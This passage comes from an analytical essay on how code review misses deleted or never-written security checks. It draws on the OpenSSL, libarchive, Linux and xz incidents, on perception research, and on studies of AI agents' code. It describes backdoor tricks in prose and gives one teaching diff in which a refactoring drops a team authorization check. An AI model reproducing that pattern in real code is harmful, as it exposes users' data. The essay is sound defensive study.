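This line appeared in two functions. In one, it added the unpredictable data that other code had supplied, which was the function's whole purpose. In the other, it added whatever was already in the memory reserved for the output, which the library didn't need.

The Debian maintainer, Kurt Roeckx, asked on an OpenSSL mailing list whether he could remove both lines. *Lessons from the Debian/OpenSSL Fiasco* (Cox, 2008) reproduces the exchange. Roeckx quoted the lines with their line numbers but did not name the functions containing them, and said he did not know what removing them would do. Someone with an OpenSSL address replied that he was in favour if it helped with debugging, and a second reply also supported the idea. Roeckx disabled both lines in Debian's copy. According to Edge (2008), in *Debian, OpenSSL, and a lack of cooperation*, he never submitted the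 change to OpenSSL, where it would probably have been examined more closely.

After that, almost the only thing that varied between keys was the number the operating system gives each running program. SSH keys, which people use to log in to remote machines, had only 32,767 possibilities for each type and size, few enough for an attacker to try them all. The flaw lasted until May 2008, when it was found by Luciano Bello. According to comments under Cox's article, he found it by accident because he needed a large supply of prime numbers and kept getting duplicates.

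This case resembles a removed security check, although the line itself neither refused nor cleaned anything. The change was visible in the patch, but its significance depended on code elsewhere. Cox believes that an OpenSSL developer who saw the old and new files side by side would probably have caught the mistake. *The actual change* (Hudson, 2008) gives a reason to doubt this. Tim Hudson, who had handled vulnerability reports for a security company's software, read the patch after the announcement and missed the problem on his first reading, even though he knew the patch contained a serious flaw. It removed the same line in two places, and he had to open the whole file to tell which removal was safe and which was not.

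There was a second chance to notice the change. Kinkhorst (2008) explains in *DSA 1571 vulnerability first introduced in 0.9.8c-1* that Debian's first attempt put the altered code in a file that the build did not use, so it had no effect. A later version moved the file to the right place, a correction that sounded harmless but activated the flaw.

### A less careful print function in libarchive

Libarchive is a library for packing and unpacking archive files. In 2021, its maintainers accepted a pull request that replaced calls to `safe_fprintf` with calls to `fprintf`. Both functions print text, but `safe_fprintf` filters out control characters, which can make a terminal do more than display text. The change slightly weakened the escaping of output, and it was plainly visible in the diff as a change of function name.

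The change stood for more than two years. In March 2024, people discovered that the same contributor had planted a backdoor (a hidden way in) in xz, a compression program. The security researcher Tavis Ormandy now had a reason to distrust the contributor. He drew attention to the old pull request on a mailing list hosted by Openwall (2024) and was able to describe the problem in a sentence.

In a reply in the oss-sec archive of that list, one poster called the change minor, since many command-line tools don't filter control characters at all, and guessed that it had been an experiment to see whether the project would accept a loss of security. Nobody has shown that, and someone who wanted a fuller error message and did not know the difference between the functions could have written the same lines. Libarchive could restore the filter without knowing the intent, but the suspicion led it to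 review all of the contributor's other work, according to a patch in the GNU bug tracker written while that review was under way.

The repair is as easy to overlook as the original change. The version of the repair that went into FreeBSD's *tar*, a tool for unpacking archives, has a title about more robust error reporting that does not mention security.

### Inserted code in Linux and xz

Neither of the two best-known attempts to plant a backdoor in Linux software is a clear example of reviewers catching a hostile addition, which we would expect if such additions are easier to notice than missing checks.

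In November 2003 an intruder added two lines to a copy of the Linux kernel's source code. By the usual account, the developers kept the main version in one version-control system and offered the copy in another for people who preferred it. A routine comparison, rather than anyone reading the code, revealed that the copy contained a change missing from the main version. Once the discrepancy reached the kernel's mailing list, readers soon worked out what the lines did. They looked like a check that rejects an invalid combination of options, but they used a single equals sign where a comparison needs two, and so gave administrator rights to any program that used that combination.

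The readers' success in the Linux case supports the idea that people can recognise hostile code once they see it, but they already knew something was wrong. Hudson also knew something was wrong when he read the Debian patch, and he missed the problem at first. Two examples are too few for a good comparison, and Ormandy quickly diagnosed the libarchive change, which suggests that weakened protections aren't always harder to recognise than hostile code. The Linux case also doesn't show whether an ordinary review would have caught the hostile lines, because they never went through one. They were disguised as a check, which might have reassured a reviewer who was skimming for checks.

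The xz backdoor reached users, mostly those running test versions of Linux systems. Its author had contributed to the project for about two years and become one of its maintainers, who could release code without independent review. Most of the hostile code was inside compressed files disguised as test data. The instructions that unpacked it were in the downloadable release but not in the public repository. Someone who read every diff in the repository would have seen some new test files but nothing recognisable as an attack. Andres Freund, a database developer, discovered the backdoor because logins were using too much processor time and Valgrind was reporting errors.

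The xz case shows that inserted code is not always easy to see. The mailing line in the document application is easy to spot because it is plain code in a file that people review. An attacker could hide the same instruction from reviewers by putting it in a compressed file, or in a release that nobody compares with the repository. Comparing each release with its source, as the Linux developers compared their two sets of records, could have exposed the extra instructions in xz. It would not have exposed the libarchive change, which was in the repository for everyone to read.

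## Why an absence is harder to notice than an addition

Reviewers may miss an absent check for several reasons. People may notice an added thing more readily than a missing one. A reviewer may not know that the code needs a check there. The check may be in another file, so its absence from the diff doesn't show that it is missing. And a program without the check still works, so nothing prompts anyone to look for the gap. The reason matters because a clearer display could help reviewers who overlook a gap but not those who don't know a check is needed.

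### Circles and pigeons

Treisman and Souther (1985), in *Search Asymmetry*, showed eight students cards with one, six or twelve circles and had them press a key to indicate whether each card contained a target. In one condition, the target was a circle with a short vertical line through its edge, and the rest were plain. In the other, the target was a plain circle among circles with lines.

The line was easy to find. Each extra plain circle added about 4 milliseconds to the search, so twelve circles took hardly longer than one. When the target was the plain circle, each extra item added about 20 milliseconds, or about 39 if the card contained no target. We would expect this if people check the circles one at a time, stop when they find the target, and go through the whole card when there isn't one. The students also missed 13.9% of the plain targets on cards with twelve circles, while error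 rates in all the other conditions were below 4%.

Psychologists call this a search asymmetry. Treisman and Souther explain it by proposing that the visual system registers simple features across the whole view at once, so a viewer can tell that one circle has a line without checking each circle. When every circle but one has a line, detecting lines doesn't reveal the exception, and the viewer has to inspect each circle to find it.

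Animals show a related bias, the feature-positive effect. They learn more easily when the presence of something signals a reward than when its absence does. In a typical experiment, a pigeon pecks at a green key that sometimes has a small white square on it. Pigeons soon learn the pattern if food comes only when the square is there, but they often learn little or nothing if food comes only when it is missing.

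In that design, though, the square is also missing between trials, when no food ever comes, so its absence is a poor predictor of food. Hearst and Wolff (1989), in *Addition versus deletion as a signal*, removed the gaps between trials to make appearance and disappearance equally good predictors. Appearance still worked better. By the fourth day of one comparison, all seven birds that had to watch for the square to appear made at least 90% of their pecks at the right time, compared with one of the seven that had to watch for it to disappear. The slower birds kept improving over the 20 days of training, so they could learn from an absence, but more slowly.

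The nearest equivalent in code review is a pull request that adds twelve similar routes in one new file, where only eleven begin with the team condition. The reviewer is searching for a plain circle among circles with lines, and has to check every route. The missing check in the export route is even harder to notice, because the diff shows that route alone, with no guarded routes to compare it with. The students also knew which kind of circle to look for, whereas nobody tells a reviewer whether a check is missing, or which one.

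When a change removes a check, the diff still displays the deleted condition, usually in red. The reviewer has something visible to find, so search asymmetry, the greater difficulty of spotting an absent feature than a present one, can't explain why they would miss it.

A weakened check doesn't leave a gap either. Treisman and Souther distinguish features that can disappear without a replacement, like the line, from features like colour, where something that stops being red must become another colour. The loosened condition in the document application is more like a change of colour, because a login test has replaced the team test and the reviewer has to judge whether the login test is good enough.

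### Objects added to a scene or taken away

Psychologists have also tested people with everyday objects. In one set of experiments, adults who compared two similar pictures found the difference more often and more quickly when the second picture had an extra item than when it lacked one. Other adults saw a dinner place setting with 15 items and a version with 9. They identified more of the six items that differed when the experimenters had added them than when the experimenters had removed them.

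Memory may partly explain why absences are harder to notice. Someone who can no longer see the first version can see the added items but must recall the missing ones. Reviewers reading a diff have less to remember because it shows the deleted lines.

In *Detection and identification of change in naturalistic scenes*, Mondy and Coltheart (2000) found the reverse. People who viewed successive photographs of natural scenes identified deleted objects more accurately than added ones. This was true of both whole objects and parts of objects, unless the scene still contained an item identical to the deleted one. In earlier experiments with line drawings, deletions were easier to identify for parts of objects, but additions were easier for whole objects.

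Nobody has shown that the finding about unique objects applies to code. If it does, reviewers would notice the loss of a distinctive check more easily than the loss of one of many similar checks. Authorization checks are often nearly identical, with one for each route.

Donaldson and Yamamoto (2012), in *Detection of Object Onset and Offset in Naturalistic Scenes*, controlled the pictures more tightly. They photographed a table with seven or eight toys and small household goods on it. Participants saw one photograph for 1.2 seconds, a blank screen for 0.1 seconds, and then a second photograph with one object more or one fewer. They then pressed a key to show which side of the table had changed. The researchers used every pair of photographs in both orders, so eye-catching objects appeared as often as they vanished.

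The 11 participants in the analysis responded faster to appearances (668 milliseconds on average) than to disappearances (714 milliseconds). They were also slightly more accurate on appearances (97.3% versus 96.2%), but that difference could easily be chance.

Donaldson and Yamamoto also describe two earlier experiments that showed an advantage for additions. Cole and colleagues photographed household objects from above, and people were more accurate at detecting objects that appeared than objects that vanished. Brockmole and Henderson recorded eye movements, and people tended to look sooner at the place where an object had appeared than at the place where one had vanished.

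Donaldson and Yamamoto suggest that Mondy and Coltheart's result may have arisen because digital editing left unusually sharp edges in the photographs, or because people took longer over deletions and so got more of them right. Neither readily explains why a second, identical object should remove the advantage for deletions. Additions were still easier to notice in most of the experiments, but the exceptions are hard to dismiss.

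### From pictures to diffs

A 46-millisecond advantage is unlikely to matter to someone who spends several minutes on a pull request. The participants in that experiment knew that every trial contained a change. They had just over a second to look at each photograph, while a diff stays on the screen for as long as the reviewer wants.

The possible causes of the advantage don't apply well to deleted lines in a diff either. Donaldson and Yamamoto suggest that a new object draws attention in a way that a vanished one does not, or produces a larger change in the light reaching the eye. A diff shows a deleted line as a new coloured object on the page, so the deletion should benefit from both effects.

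The logic of the circle experiment applies equally to reading code. A person can confirm that something is present by finding it once, but to confirm that it is absent, they have to look everywhere it could be. However, the error rate for circles isn't a basis for predicting the error rate for routes.

Eye tracking provides some direct evidence about what people look at in code. Researchers record fixations, the moments when the eye rests on one point. *Same Scrutiny, More Time* (2026), a study of code review, adds up the time in pauses longer than 200 milliseconds to measure how long a developer spends on a piece of code.

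In *An Eye-Tracking Study on the Use of Split/Unified Code Change Views* (2023), Sandoval Alcocer, Cossio-Chavalier and colleagues asked 12 people to find bugs in two commits. Each participant used GitHub's unified view, which shows old and new lines in one column, and its split view, which shows the old version on the left and the new one on the right. Participants looked mainly at conditionals, class and object variables, and the changed code. The researchers report less visual strain with the unified view. They found no statistically significant differences between the views, but with 12 participants they could have missed any difference that wasn't large.

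The deleted team condition and the loosened one are both conditionals on changed lines. If other reviewers behave like these 12, they look at such lines, so when they approve the change anyway, they have probably failed to work out what the line means. Tim Hudson's first reading of the Debian patch fits this explanation.

The export route contains no conditional for a reviewer to notice. The habit of looking at conditionals helps reviewers judge existing checks, but it won't lead them to a missing one.

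### Knowing what belongs there

To see that something is missing, a reviewer has to compare the code with an expectation of what belongs there. The export route needs a team condition and doesn't have one, but it also lacks an unlimited number of things it doesn't need, such as currency conversion or a spelling check.

Reviewers have to know for themselves that the export route should have a check, whereas they can see the deleted condition in the diff's minus lines. Lack of knowledge therefore better explains why reviewers miss checks that were never written than why they miss checks that were removed. It could also explain why the libarchive change got through, if its reviewers didn't know how the two print functions differ.

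But people also miss omissions when they know enough to catch them. Everyone who reviewed the Java holiday program presumably knew that an employee can't take minus ten days off, yet two-thirds of the people who received that version didn't notice that the code allowed it.

An experiment on judgement may help explain this. Cherubini, Rusconi and colleagues, in *Missing the dog that failed to bark in the nighttime*, gave 126 people problems about two decks of 100 cards with letters printed on them. A table showed how common each letter was in each deck. The researchers then listed which letters were on a card from a randomly chosen deck and which were missing from it, and asked which deck the card had most likely come from.

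Here is an example with invented numbers. The letter B is on 60 cards in deck 1 and 40 in deck 2. The letter C is on 90 cards in deck 1 and 20 in deck 2. The card has a B but no C. The B slightly favours deck 1. The lack of a C strongly favours deck 2, because only 10 cards in deck 1 lack a C and 80 in deck 2 do. As the letters occur independently, we can multiply the probabilities:

odds of deck 1 against deck 2 = (0.6 × 0.1) / (0.4 × 0.8) ≈ 0.19

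Deck 2 is thus more than five times as likely. Someone who considered only the B would choose deck 1.

In every problem, the present letters were evidence for one deck and the missing letters were evidence for the other. Participants relied too much on the present letters, even when the table gave the number of cards that lacked each letter, which made the absences as easy to look up as possible. Those who more often chose the deck favored by the present letters also tended to be more confident.

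The participants had all the facts, so neither poor eyesight nor ignorance explains the result. A reviewer who knows that documents belong to teams might likewise give too much weight to the login requirement and the tidy code, and too little to the missing condition. This extrapolates from students solving abstract puzzles, and reviewers may do better with code they know.

In later experiments of the same kind, the bias was smaller when participants also saw the figures for absences and the absence of one feature meant the visible presence of another, as with colours. A weakened check might therefore be easier to judge than one that was never written, because the reviewer can see what replaced the team test, but only if they know why the team test was there.

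Professional experience may also help. Cherubini and colleagues cite a 1981 study by Christensen-Szalansky and Bushyhead in which physicians making diagnoses in a real clinic did not significantly undervalue absent symptoms. Christensen-Szalansky and Bushyhead were cautious about this result because the absence of one symptom might regularly have coincided with the presence of another, and the physicians might have been responding to the symptom that was present.

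### Checks in other files

A reviewer may notice that the export route has no team condition and still say nothing, because the application might apply that condition centrally.

Suppose that nine out of ten routes with no visible check in a project are covered by a central one (again an invented figure). A reviewer who objects to every such route will be wrong nine times out of ten and will annoy colleagues, so the reviewer can reasonably assume that the next one is covered too. Unlike the participants in the card experiment, this reviewer isn't undervaluing an absence, because a missing check is only weak evidence that a route is unprotected until someone has searched the other files.

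Fox, Markham and colleagues (2026) had a similar problem with medical notes in *LLM Judges Verify Presence, Not Absence*. To test whether language models would notice a missing fact, they tried to remove known facts from complete notes. Of the 1,791 facts they located in complete notes, 574 (32%) appeared in more than one place. Of 126 attempts to remove a fact completely, 55 failed, mostly because the fact was still somewhere in the note or the note no longer read naturally.

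They also asked a physician on their team to judge ten possible omissions, showing only part of the note for eight of them. The physician declined to answer two of those eight, and commented on one that they would need to see more of the note. Code reviewers have the same problem when they read a diff without opening the other files.

When a change deletes or loosens a condition, the reviewer may also have to look in other files for the answer, but the diff shows which rule to search for. With the export route, the reviewer has to think of the rule before searching for it.

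No experiment seems to have isolated this effect by giving reviewers the same omission with the relevant file open and with it closed. The Chromium OS finding about directories is consistent with it, but can't separate the effect of scattered code from the effect of long changes.

### Features that work without their checks

An author who has just written the export feature will probably test whether it exports documents:

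```python
def test_owner_can_export():
    log_in(owner)
    assert get("/documents/7/export").status_code == 200
```

Code 200 means success. The test passes with or without the team condition because it doesn't include a user who should be refused. The testers in the student contest likewise logged in only as the owner.

This helps explain how missing checks survive, but not why reviewers would notice hostile additions more readily. A test like this one would also pass if the route emailed every document to an outsider. Unlike a missing check, though, the line that sends the emails is visible to a reviewer who reads the diff.

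Tests are more likely to catch a removed check than one that was never written. If the project already has a test that expects a 403 error for a user from another team, deleting the team check will make that test fail, unless the author changes the test as well. Loosening the check to allow any logged-in user will also make that test fail, but it won't affect a test that only tries a visitor who is not logged in. A new route has no existing tests, so none will fail if the author never writes the check.

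### Physicians reviewing drafts

People may be no worse at noticing absences than other mistakes when they check ordinary writing. Biro and colleagues planted mistakes in AI-drafted replies to patients and asked physicians to review them. Fox and colleagues report that the physicians caught omissions about as often as objective errors, roughly a quarter to a third of each. They take this as a sign that a particular weakness at spotting omissions is specific to language models, which have no text to examine where something is missing, rather than common to all reviewers. They call the comparison only indicative because the physicians and the models did different tasks with different material.

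The result is a good reason not to treat the asymmetry as a law of human perception, but it is weaker evidence about code. Equal detection rates depend partly on which mistakes the researchers planted, and more glaring errors might have produced a gap. A wrong fact in a message can also look ordinary, like the unchecked subtraction in the holiday program, whereas the mailing line looks suspicious to anyone who reads it. So the physicians may have needed knowledge of the patient to catch either kind of mistake.

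The other published figures that Fox and colleagues collected vary a good deal. In one study, clinicians who had the source document beside them found 50.4% of omissions. In another, twelve radiologists looking for words missing from text caught 61.8% of them on average, with a range of 42% to 92%. The tasks are too different for a strict comparison, but both groups had help that the reviewer of the export route lacks. The clinicians could compare the text with its source, and the radiologists could find the gaps from the text itself, much as a programmer can see that code opens a file and never closes it.

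## Why AI-generated changes make missing checks harder to see

Someone who asks a coding agent for a way to export documents probably won't mention teams. The agent has to work out that the route needs the team condition, and if it leaves the condition out, the export still works. In tests, recent models often leave out protections nobody asked for. AI-written changes may also make such gaps harder to notice in review, but researchers have measured only some of the possible reasons.

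### How often models leave out checks

The most direct tests run the generated program and attack it. The BaxBench benchmark gives a model the specification of a web application's server side, checks that the result works, and then tries real exploits on it. In *Applying Security by Design at the Point of Execution*, Farinha (2026) used BaxBench to test two of Anthropic's models with prompts that did not mention security. Claude Opus 4.5 produced 26 working applications from 28 specifications, and at least one exploit succeeded against 9 of the 26 (35%). For Claude Opus 4.7, working as an agent, exploits succeeded against 7 of 23 working applications in one web framework (30%) and 6 of 24 in another (25%).

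A successful exploit doesn't always mean that a check is missing. Farinha gives some results by type of flaw for a second benchmark, DualGauge, in which Claude Opus 4.7 wrote 59 short Python programs and another model judged how they behaved under attack. These are the three types with the largest changes after Farinha gave the model written security requirements:

| Attack | Protection needed | Security tests passed, no requirements given | Passed, requirements given |
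|---|---|---|---|
| A file name leads outside the permitted folder (path traversal) | Input validation | 16 of 34 | 30 of 34 |
| Input forges entries in a log | Escaping or validation | 0 of 9 | 9 of 9 |
| Input runs as code in a browser (cross-site scripting) | Escaping | 14 of 19 | 19 of 19 |

Farinha singled out these types for their large gains, so they make the model look worse than it was overall. Across all types, the code passed 287 of 371 security tests (77%) without the requirements and 345 (93%) with them.

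The requirements, which came from a manual that Farinha wrote, contained no code to copy. So in many cases the model could write the protection but had not inferred that the task required it.

On BaxBench, stating requirements raised the share of Opus 4.5's working applications that withstood every exploit from 65% to 86%, but it lowered the number that worked from 26 to 21. Some of the stricter applications failed only because they rejected something used in the benchmark's tests, such as a five-character password.

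Models also have trouble finding gaps in code that already exists. *SecProbe* (Luo, Huang and colleagues, 2026) planted flaws of 151 types in working projects and asked agents to find and repair them. The best combination of model and agent software succeeded on 28% of the tasks. The tasks were meant to be hard, and a repair counted only if it blocked the prepared attacks and kept the program working.

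### Missing authorization in deployed applications

Farinha's results by type don't cover authorization. The best evidence on that comes from Deng, Fan and Meng's *Understanding the (In)Security of Vibe-Coded Applications* (2026). They collected applications that people had built almost entirely with Claude Code or with Lovable, a service that builds applications from descriptions, and picked 200 at random from the web applications that were live. Two AI agents each audited every application twice. Another agent then tried to confirm the reported flaws, where possible with harmless requests to the live site, and two of the researchers reviewed what was left.

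Deng and colleagues confirmed 1,186 flaws, about six per application, and 91% of the applications had at least one. The flaws were concentrated in broken access control, injection and authentication failures. Broken access control includes both missing authorization and checks that are present but wrong. As an example from outside their sample, they cite a published vulnerability in sites generated by Lovable. The sites' databases had inadequate rules about who could read which rows, so visitors could read other people's data without logging in.

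Many owners of such applications have little programming experience and may never have read the code. The audit therefore shows which checks agents leave out when perhaps nobody reviews their work. It covered only AI-built applications, so it can't show whether people would have left out fewer.

In *From Preventive to Reactive*, a 2026 study of how AI assistants affect developers' attention to security, an assistant wrote code for updating a user's profile that took the user's identifier from the request instead of from the login session. The code lacked an authorization check, so anyone could change anyone else's profile (CWE-639). One participant noticed the flaw immediately. Another learned of a security concern by asking the assistant whether there were any more. In the other 12 of the 14 sessions, participants either did not review for security or were satisfied with code that still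 had vulnerabilities.

*Security Vulnerability Patterns in AI-Generated Code* (Kahn and Hastings, 2026) reports 45 flaws in nine office-automation scripts, but this count can't serve as a rate because the study capped the number of flaws per script. Kahn and Hastings asked ChatGPT, Microsoft Copilot and Google Gemini for three scripts each, and asked the reviewing model, Claude Code, for no more than five flaws per script. The total is exactly five for each script. The flaws included web addresses and file paths that the scripts used without validation.

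### What happens to agents' pull requests

Several studies use AIDev, a public collection of pull requests by coding agents. They mostly use a subset of 33,596 pull requests to popular GitHub projects, which OpenAI Codex, GitHub Copilot, Devin, Cursor and Claude Code opened from December 2024 to the summer of 2025. These agents have changed a good deal since then.

*Insights into Security-Related AI-Generated Pull Requests* (Rabbi, Turzo and colleagues, 2026) examines 675 AI-generated pull requests that concerned security, which the researchers selected using keywords and then a language model. Projects merged 354 (52%), closed 219 without merging and left 102 open. The researchers ran Semgrep, a static analysis tool, on each project before and after the change. 104 of the pull requests (15%) added at least one warning.

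The most common type of warning, with 306 of the 853, was for text-matching patterns slow enough for an attacker to tie up the program. These patterns aren't missing checks, and 289 of the 306 warnings came from Copilot pull requests that projects rejected. About a third of the 853 warnings were for command injection (110), path traversal (87), cross-site scripting (60), SQL injection (17) or improper escaping (16), which usually do result from missing validation or escaping.

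Warnings about improper authorization were rare, ten at most, but Deng and colleagues found access control to be one of the main problems in AI-built applications. The difference probably comes more from the methods than from the code. Semgrep mostly searches for recognisable dangerous patterns, and the export route contains none.

The warnings seem to have had little to do with what projects merged. Adding up the figures that Rabbi and colleagues give for each agent produces these totals:

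| Outcome | Pull requests | With at least one new warning |
|---|---|---|
| Merged | 354 | 51 (14%) |
| Closed without merging | 219 | 29 (13%) |
| Still open | 102 | 24 (24%) |

Some of the warnings must have been false alarms, and reviewers may have had good reason to ignore them. Rabbi and colleagues also found that projects often closed pull requests for other reasons, such as inactivity or missing tests. Even so, a merge was no sign that the change was free of new warnings.

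In *Security in the Age of AI Teammates*, Siddiq, Zhao and colleagues (2026) manually reviewed the candidates from the same collection and identified 1,293 pull requests whose main purpose was security. Of those no longer open, projects had merged 61.5%, compared with 77.3% of agents' other pull requests. The 61.5% figure agrees with that of Rabbi and colleagues, which is 62% if open pull requests are left out. The median time from opening to closing was 3.9 hours for security pull requests and about seven minutes for the others.

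Much of the gap in merge rates comes from the mix of agents rather than from extra care over security. Codex opened about two-thirds of all the pull requests. Projects merged most of them, and few concerned security. The merge rate for security pull requests was lower than for the same agent's other pull requests by 15 percentage points for Claude Code, 6 for Copilot and 4 for Devin. It was slightly higher for Codex and Cursor.

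Extra care over security changes wouldn't help with the export route, because it would be described as adding an export feature. That puts it among the ordinary pull requests, which had a median of seven minutes. Some developers may have read the agent's code before opening the pull request, so seven minutes may not be all the attention a change received.

### A deleted check among other deletions

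Refactoring means restructuring code without changing what it does. It deletes and rewrites many lines, so a lost check can be hard to pick out. Suppose that someone asks an agent to return a proper error when a document doesn't exist, and the agent also moves the lookup into a shared function:

```diff
+def load_document(doc_id):
+    doc = Document.get(doc_id)
+    if doc is None:
+        abort(404)
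+    return doc
+
 @app.get("/documents/<int:doc_id>")
 def show_document(doc_id):
-    doc = Document.get(doc_id)
-    if doc.team_id != current_user.team_id:
-        abort(403)
-    return page(doc)
+    return page(load_document(doc_id))
```

A request for a nonexistent document now gets error 404 ("not found"), as intended. Of the four deleted lines, the lookup and the final return reappear elsewhere, but the team condition and its refusal do not. A reviewer in a hurry could mistake the new function's condition and `abort` for the old check. To notice the loss, the reviewer has to account for each deleted line.

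*Refactoring Runaway* (Tian, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) found that agents mixed refactoring into their patches less often than humans did, contrary to the common complaint. It compared 3,691 agent-written patches with human fixes for the same 128 Java issues, none of which asked for refactoring. The agents used twelve models, including Claude 3.7 Sonnet and Gemini 2.5 Pro. Refactoring appeared in 21% of the agents' patches and 37% of the human ones, with averages of 0.66 and 1.75 refactoring operations per patch.

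Agents sometimes change far more than they were asked to. Tian and colleagues describe an agent that was asked to remove three lines of unused code and changed 16,881 lines in 89 files. Nobody could review that properly, but it is also too conspicuous to get through review unnoticed. Smaller mixtures like the one above are probably the greater risk, whoever writes them.

Reviewers can't always tell from the description of a commit (a saved set of edits) that it includes refactoring. In *Agentic Refactoring*, Horikawa, Li and colleagues (2026) found 51,412 refactoring operations in agents' Java commits. Of these, 18,801 (37%) were in commits that did not state a refactoring aim, although developers may have asked for some of them in their instructions to the agent.

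These studies measure the mixing, but not whether it makes reviewers miss a deleted check. That effect is plausible but unproven. Reviewers of Chromium OS found fewer flaws in changes that touched more directories.

In *Quality and Security Signals in AI-Generated Python Refactoring Pull Requests*, Almukhtar, Ghammam and Ming (2026) ran Bandit, a tool that warns about risky Python code, on the files that AI agents had changed in 438 refactoring pull requests. In 119 of 2,528 files (4.7%), the changes added more warnings than they removed. Projects merged 322 of the pull requests (73.5%), including 27 that introduced new Bandit warnings.

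Most of the new warnings were about risky habits, not serious vulnerabilities. The figures also don't show how often refactoring removes a check, because Bandit detects risky code that is present. If an agent deleted the team condition, Bandit would report nothing new. Programmers sometimes write checks as Python `assert` statements, which Bandit warns about, so deleting one outside the test files would count as removing a problem.

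### Fluent code and confident descriptions

Language models tend to write tidy code with sensible names and describe it well, so reviewers may assume the author has thought of everything. A careless human often leaves other signs of carelessness, but a model can omit the team condition from the export route and still produce code that looks professional.

Agarwal, Miller and colleagues (2026), in *3100 Opinions on Code Review in an AI World*, analysed blog posts and Reddit discussions about review, using language models to sort the material. Many writers said that polished code makes reviewers read less closely. Others said they had become more suspicious of AI-written code and now read every line. Agarwal and colleagues turn these opinions into claims for others to test, and say they have not confirmed any of them.

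Acceptance rates give this idea little support. Rabbi and colleagues used a trained classifier to judge whether agents' commit messages explained both what had changed and why, and 70% did. But changes with such messages weren't consistently accepted more often. Claude Code's acceptance rate was 60% with or without a full explanation. With one, Codex's rate was higher (96% versus 88%) and Devin's was much lower (37% versus 54%).

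Tests didn't seem to reassure reviewers either, since security pull requests that changed test files had about 50% lower odds of being merged than those that didn't, after allowing for other factors (odds ratio 0.51). Siddiq and colleagues also found that complexity and wordiness were associated with rejection.

None of this directly tests whether fluent writing hides missing checks. To test that, researchers would need to show reviewers the same missing check in polished and in clumsy code, with and without a confident description. The 12 participants in *From Preventive to Reactive* who missed or ignored problems might have done the same with human-written code.

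### More changes and less discussion

Agents can write changes faster than people can read them. If the number of reviewers stays the same, each change will probably get less attention. A reviewer short of time is more likely to check the lines in the diff than to search other files for a rule that the new code ignores.

Agents' pull requests get less discussion than human ones. In the history of 2,860 GitHub projects up to February 2026, Agarwal and colleagues found that half of agents' pull requests had no review comments, compared with 38% of human ones. Projects also merged agents' work faster, but the median time to merge it rose from about 20 minutes in May 2025 to between two and three hours in early 2026, while agents were becoming more common. Over roughly the same period, the share of merged agent pull requests that no human had reviewed fell from over half to about 12%, slightly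 below the rate for human-written ones.

*Habituation at the Gate* (Yu, Jia and colleagues, 2026) found a less encouraging trend among individuals. The study followed 400 people who had each reviewed at least ten agent pull requests. The overall approval rate rose from 30.1% in the first half of each person's reviews to 36.8% in the second half. Comments on specific lines fell from 1.01 per review in people's earliest reviews to 0.79 in their latest. Approval of human-written changes in the same projects fell over those months, so people were not becoming more lenient in general.

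The two studies can both be right, because projects may review more of their agents' changes while each reviewer says less about them. Yu and colleagues think reviewers most likely comment less because of habit under a growing workload. They also accept that the agents may have improved, which would make fewer comments reasonable, but they had no measure of the code's quality.

Neither study measured how long anyone spent reading. The time between opening and merging a pull request includes time spent waiting, so it can grow while reading time shrinks. Less discussion was measured, but the claims that volume causes it and that missing checks get through as a result are still inferences.

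For missing checks, who reviews a change may matter more than how long they spend on it. Agarwal and colleagues found that the developer who had set the agent to work was the only human involved in reviewing an average of 40.1% of agents' pull requests per project. For human-written pull requests, the author was the only human involved in 21.5%. Farinha's results suggest that agents often omit a check because nobody asked for it. If the person who forgot to mention teams is also the only reviewer, they could easily forget teams again when they read the diff.

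### Asking why a line went

A reviewer who notices that the team condition was removed can ask the author why. A human author can usually say whether they moved it, thought it was redundant or deleted it by mistake. When an agent made the change, the person who submitted it may not have known the condition existed. They can ask the agent why it removed the condition, but a plausible answer doesn't show that anything else enforces the rule.

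Practitioners in the material that Agarwal and colleagues collected make the related complaint that a reviewer who doesn't know what the author intended has to work that out before judging the code against it. Nobody seems to have tested this opinion either. Agents often explain their changes, giving a reason in 70% of commit messages, but the reason applies to the commit as a whole and may not cover one deleted condition.

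Human authors can't always say what a change will do either. Kurt Roeckx didn't know what effect removing the two OpenSSL lines would have, but he knew he was removing them, so he could ask about it himself.

### How often agents remove or loosen existing checks

There is very little direct evidence on whether AI-generated changes make missing checks harder to see. The studies of pull requests count scanner warnings, merges and comments, but not deleted or loosened checks. Siddiq and colleagues recorded 377 security pull requests that worked on authentication or authorization, but they selected pull requests meant to improve security, so their sample would not have included a feature that accidentally loosened a check.

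The closest evidence is about related problems, such as code that becomes less secure over repeated AI edits and agents that delete a feature to clear a tool's warning. Repository files can also contain hidden instructions for an agent to leave out checks, a risk that *Security Impact of Coding Agent's Memory Files* (2026) examines.

Researchers could measure how often agents lose security checks by collecting the conditions that agents delete or rewrite in existing projects, selecting those that had blocked requests, and finding out whether anything still enforces each rule after the change. They would need to do the same for human-written changes to the same projects to tell whether reviewers should expect more lost checks from an agent than from a colleague.

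## Directing the reviewer to look for what should be there

The easiest way to help reviewers is to ask them to look for security problems, since few seem to do so by default. Braz and Bacchelli (2022), in *Software Security during Modern Code Review*, asked 182 developers an open question about which issues they focus on in review, and 9 mentioned security. After the survey mentioned vulnerabilities, 111 said they always consider them, although some may have said so only because it sounded responsible.

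Braz and Bacchelli also interviewed ten developers, seven of whom assumed that some other component or team was responsible for security. "I am supposing that another part of the system already dealt with it," one of them said. A reviewer who assumes this will approve the export route without looking for the team condition.

### An instruction, with and without a checklist

*Less is More* (Braz, Aeberhard and colleagues, 2022) tested the effect of an instruction on 150 people, 71% of whom had at least three years of professional experience. Everyone reviewed the same 160 lines of Java, which registered new users for a web service and contained two planted flaws. The first was that the code hashed passwords with MD5, an old algorithm that attackers can break quickly. The second was that if saving a new user failed, the code logged the whole database command, including the user's email address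 and password data.

The researchers randomly assigned participants to four groups. The first group, of 33 people, received no special instruction. The second, of 41, learned that the researchers were interested in security issues and received a definition of a vulnerability. The other two groups received the same instruction plus a checklist. For one group, of 35, the checklist had 22 items, cut down from OWASP's list of 78. For the other, of 41, it had seven items, all relevant to this change and its flaws.

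| Group | Reviewers | Found the revealing log message | Found the MD5 hashing |
|---|---|---|---|
| No security instruction | 33 | 1 (3%) | 7 (21%) |
| Instruction only | 41 | 19 (46%) | 25 (61%) |
| Instruction and 22-item checklist | 35 | 16 (46%) | 20 (57%) |
| Instruction and 7-item checklist | 41 | 19 (46%) | 28 (68%) |
| The three instructed groups together | 117 | 54 (46%) | 73 (62%) |

(The paper prints 61% for the 28 of 41, but 28 of 41 is 68%.)

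Braz and colleagues write that instructed reviewers were eight times more likely to detect a vulnerability. This is another odds ratio that reads like a ratio of rates. It appears to come from counting the people who found at least one flaw, who were 84 of the 117 instructed reviewers and 8 of the other 33:

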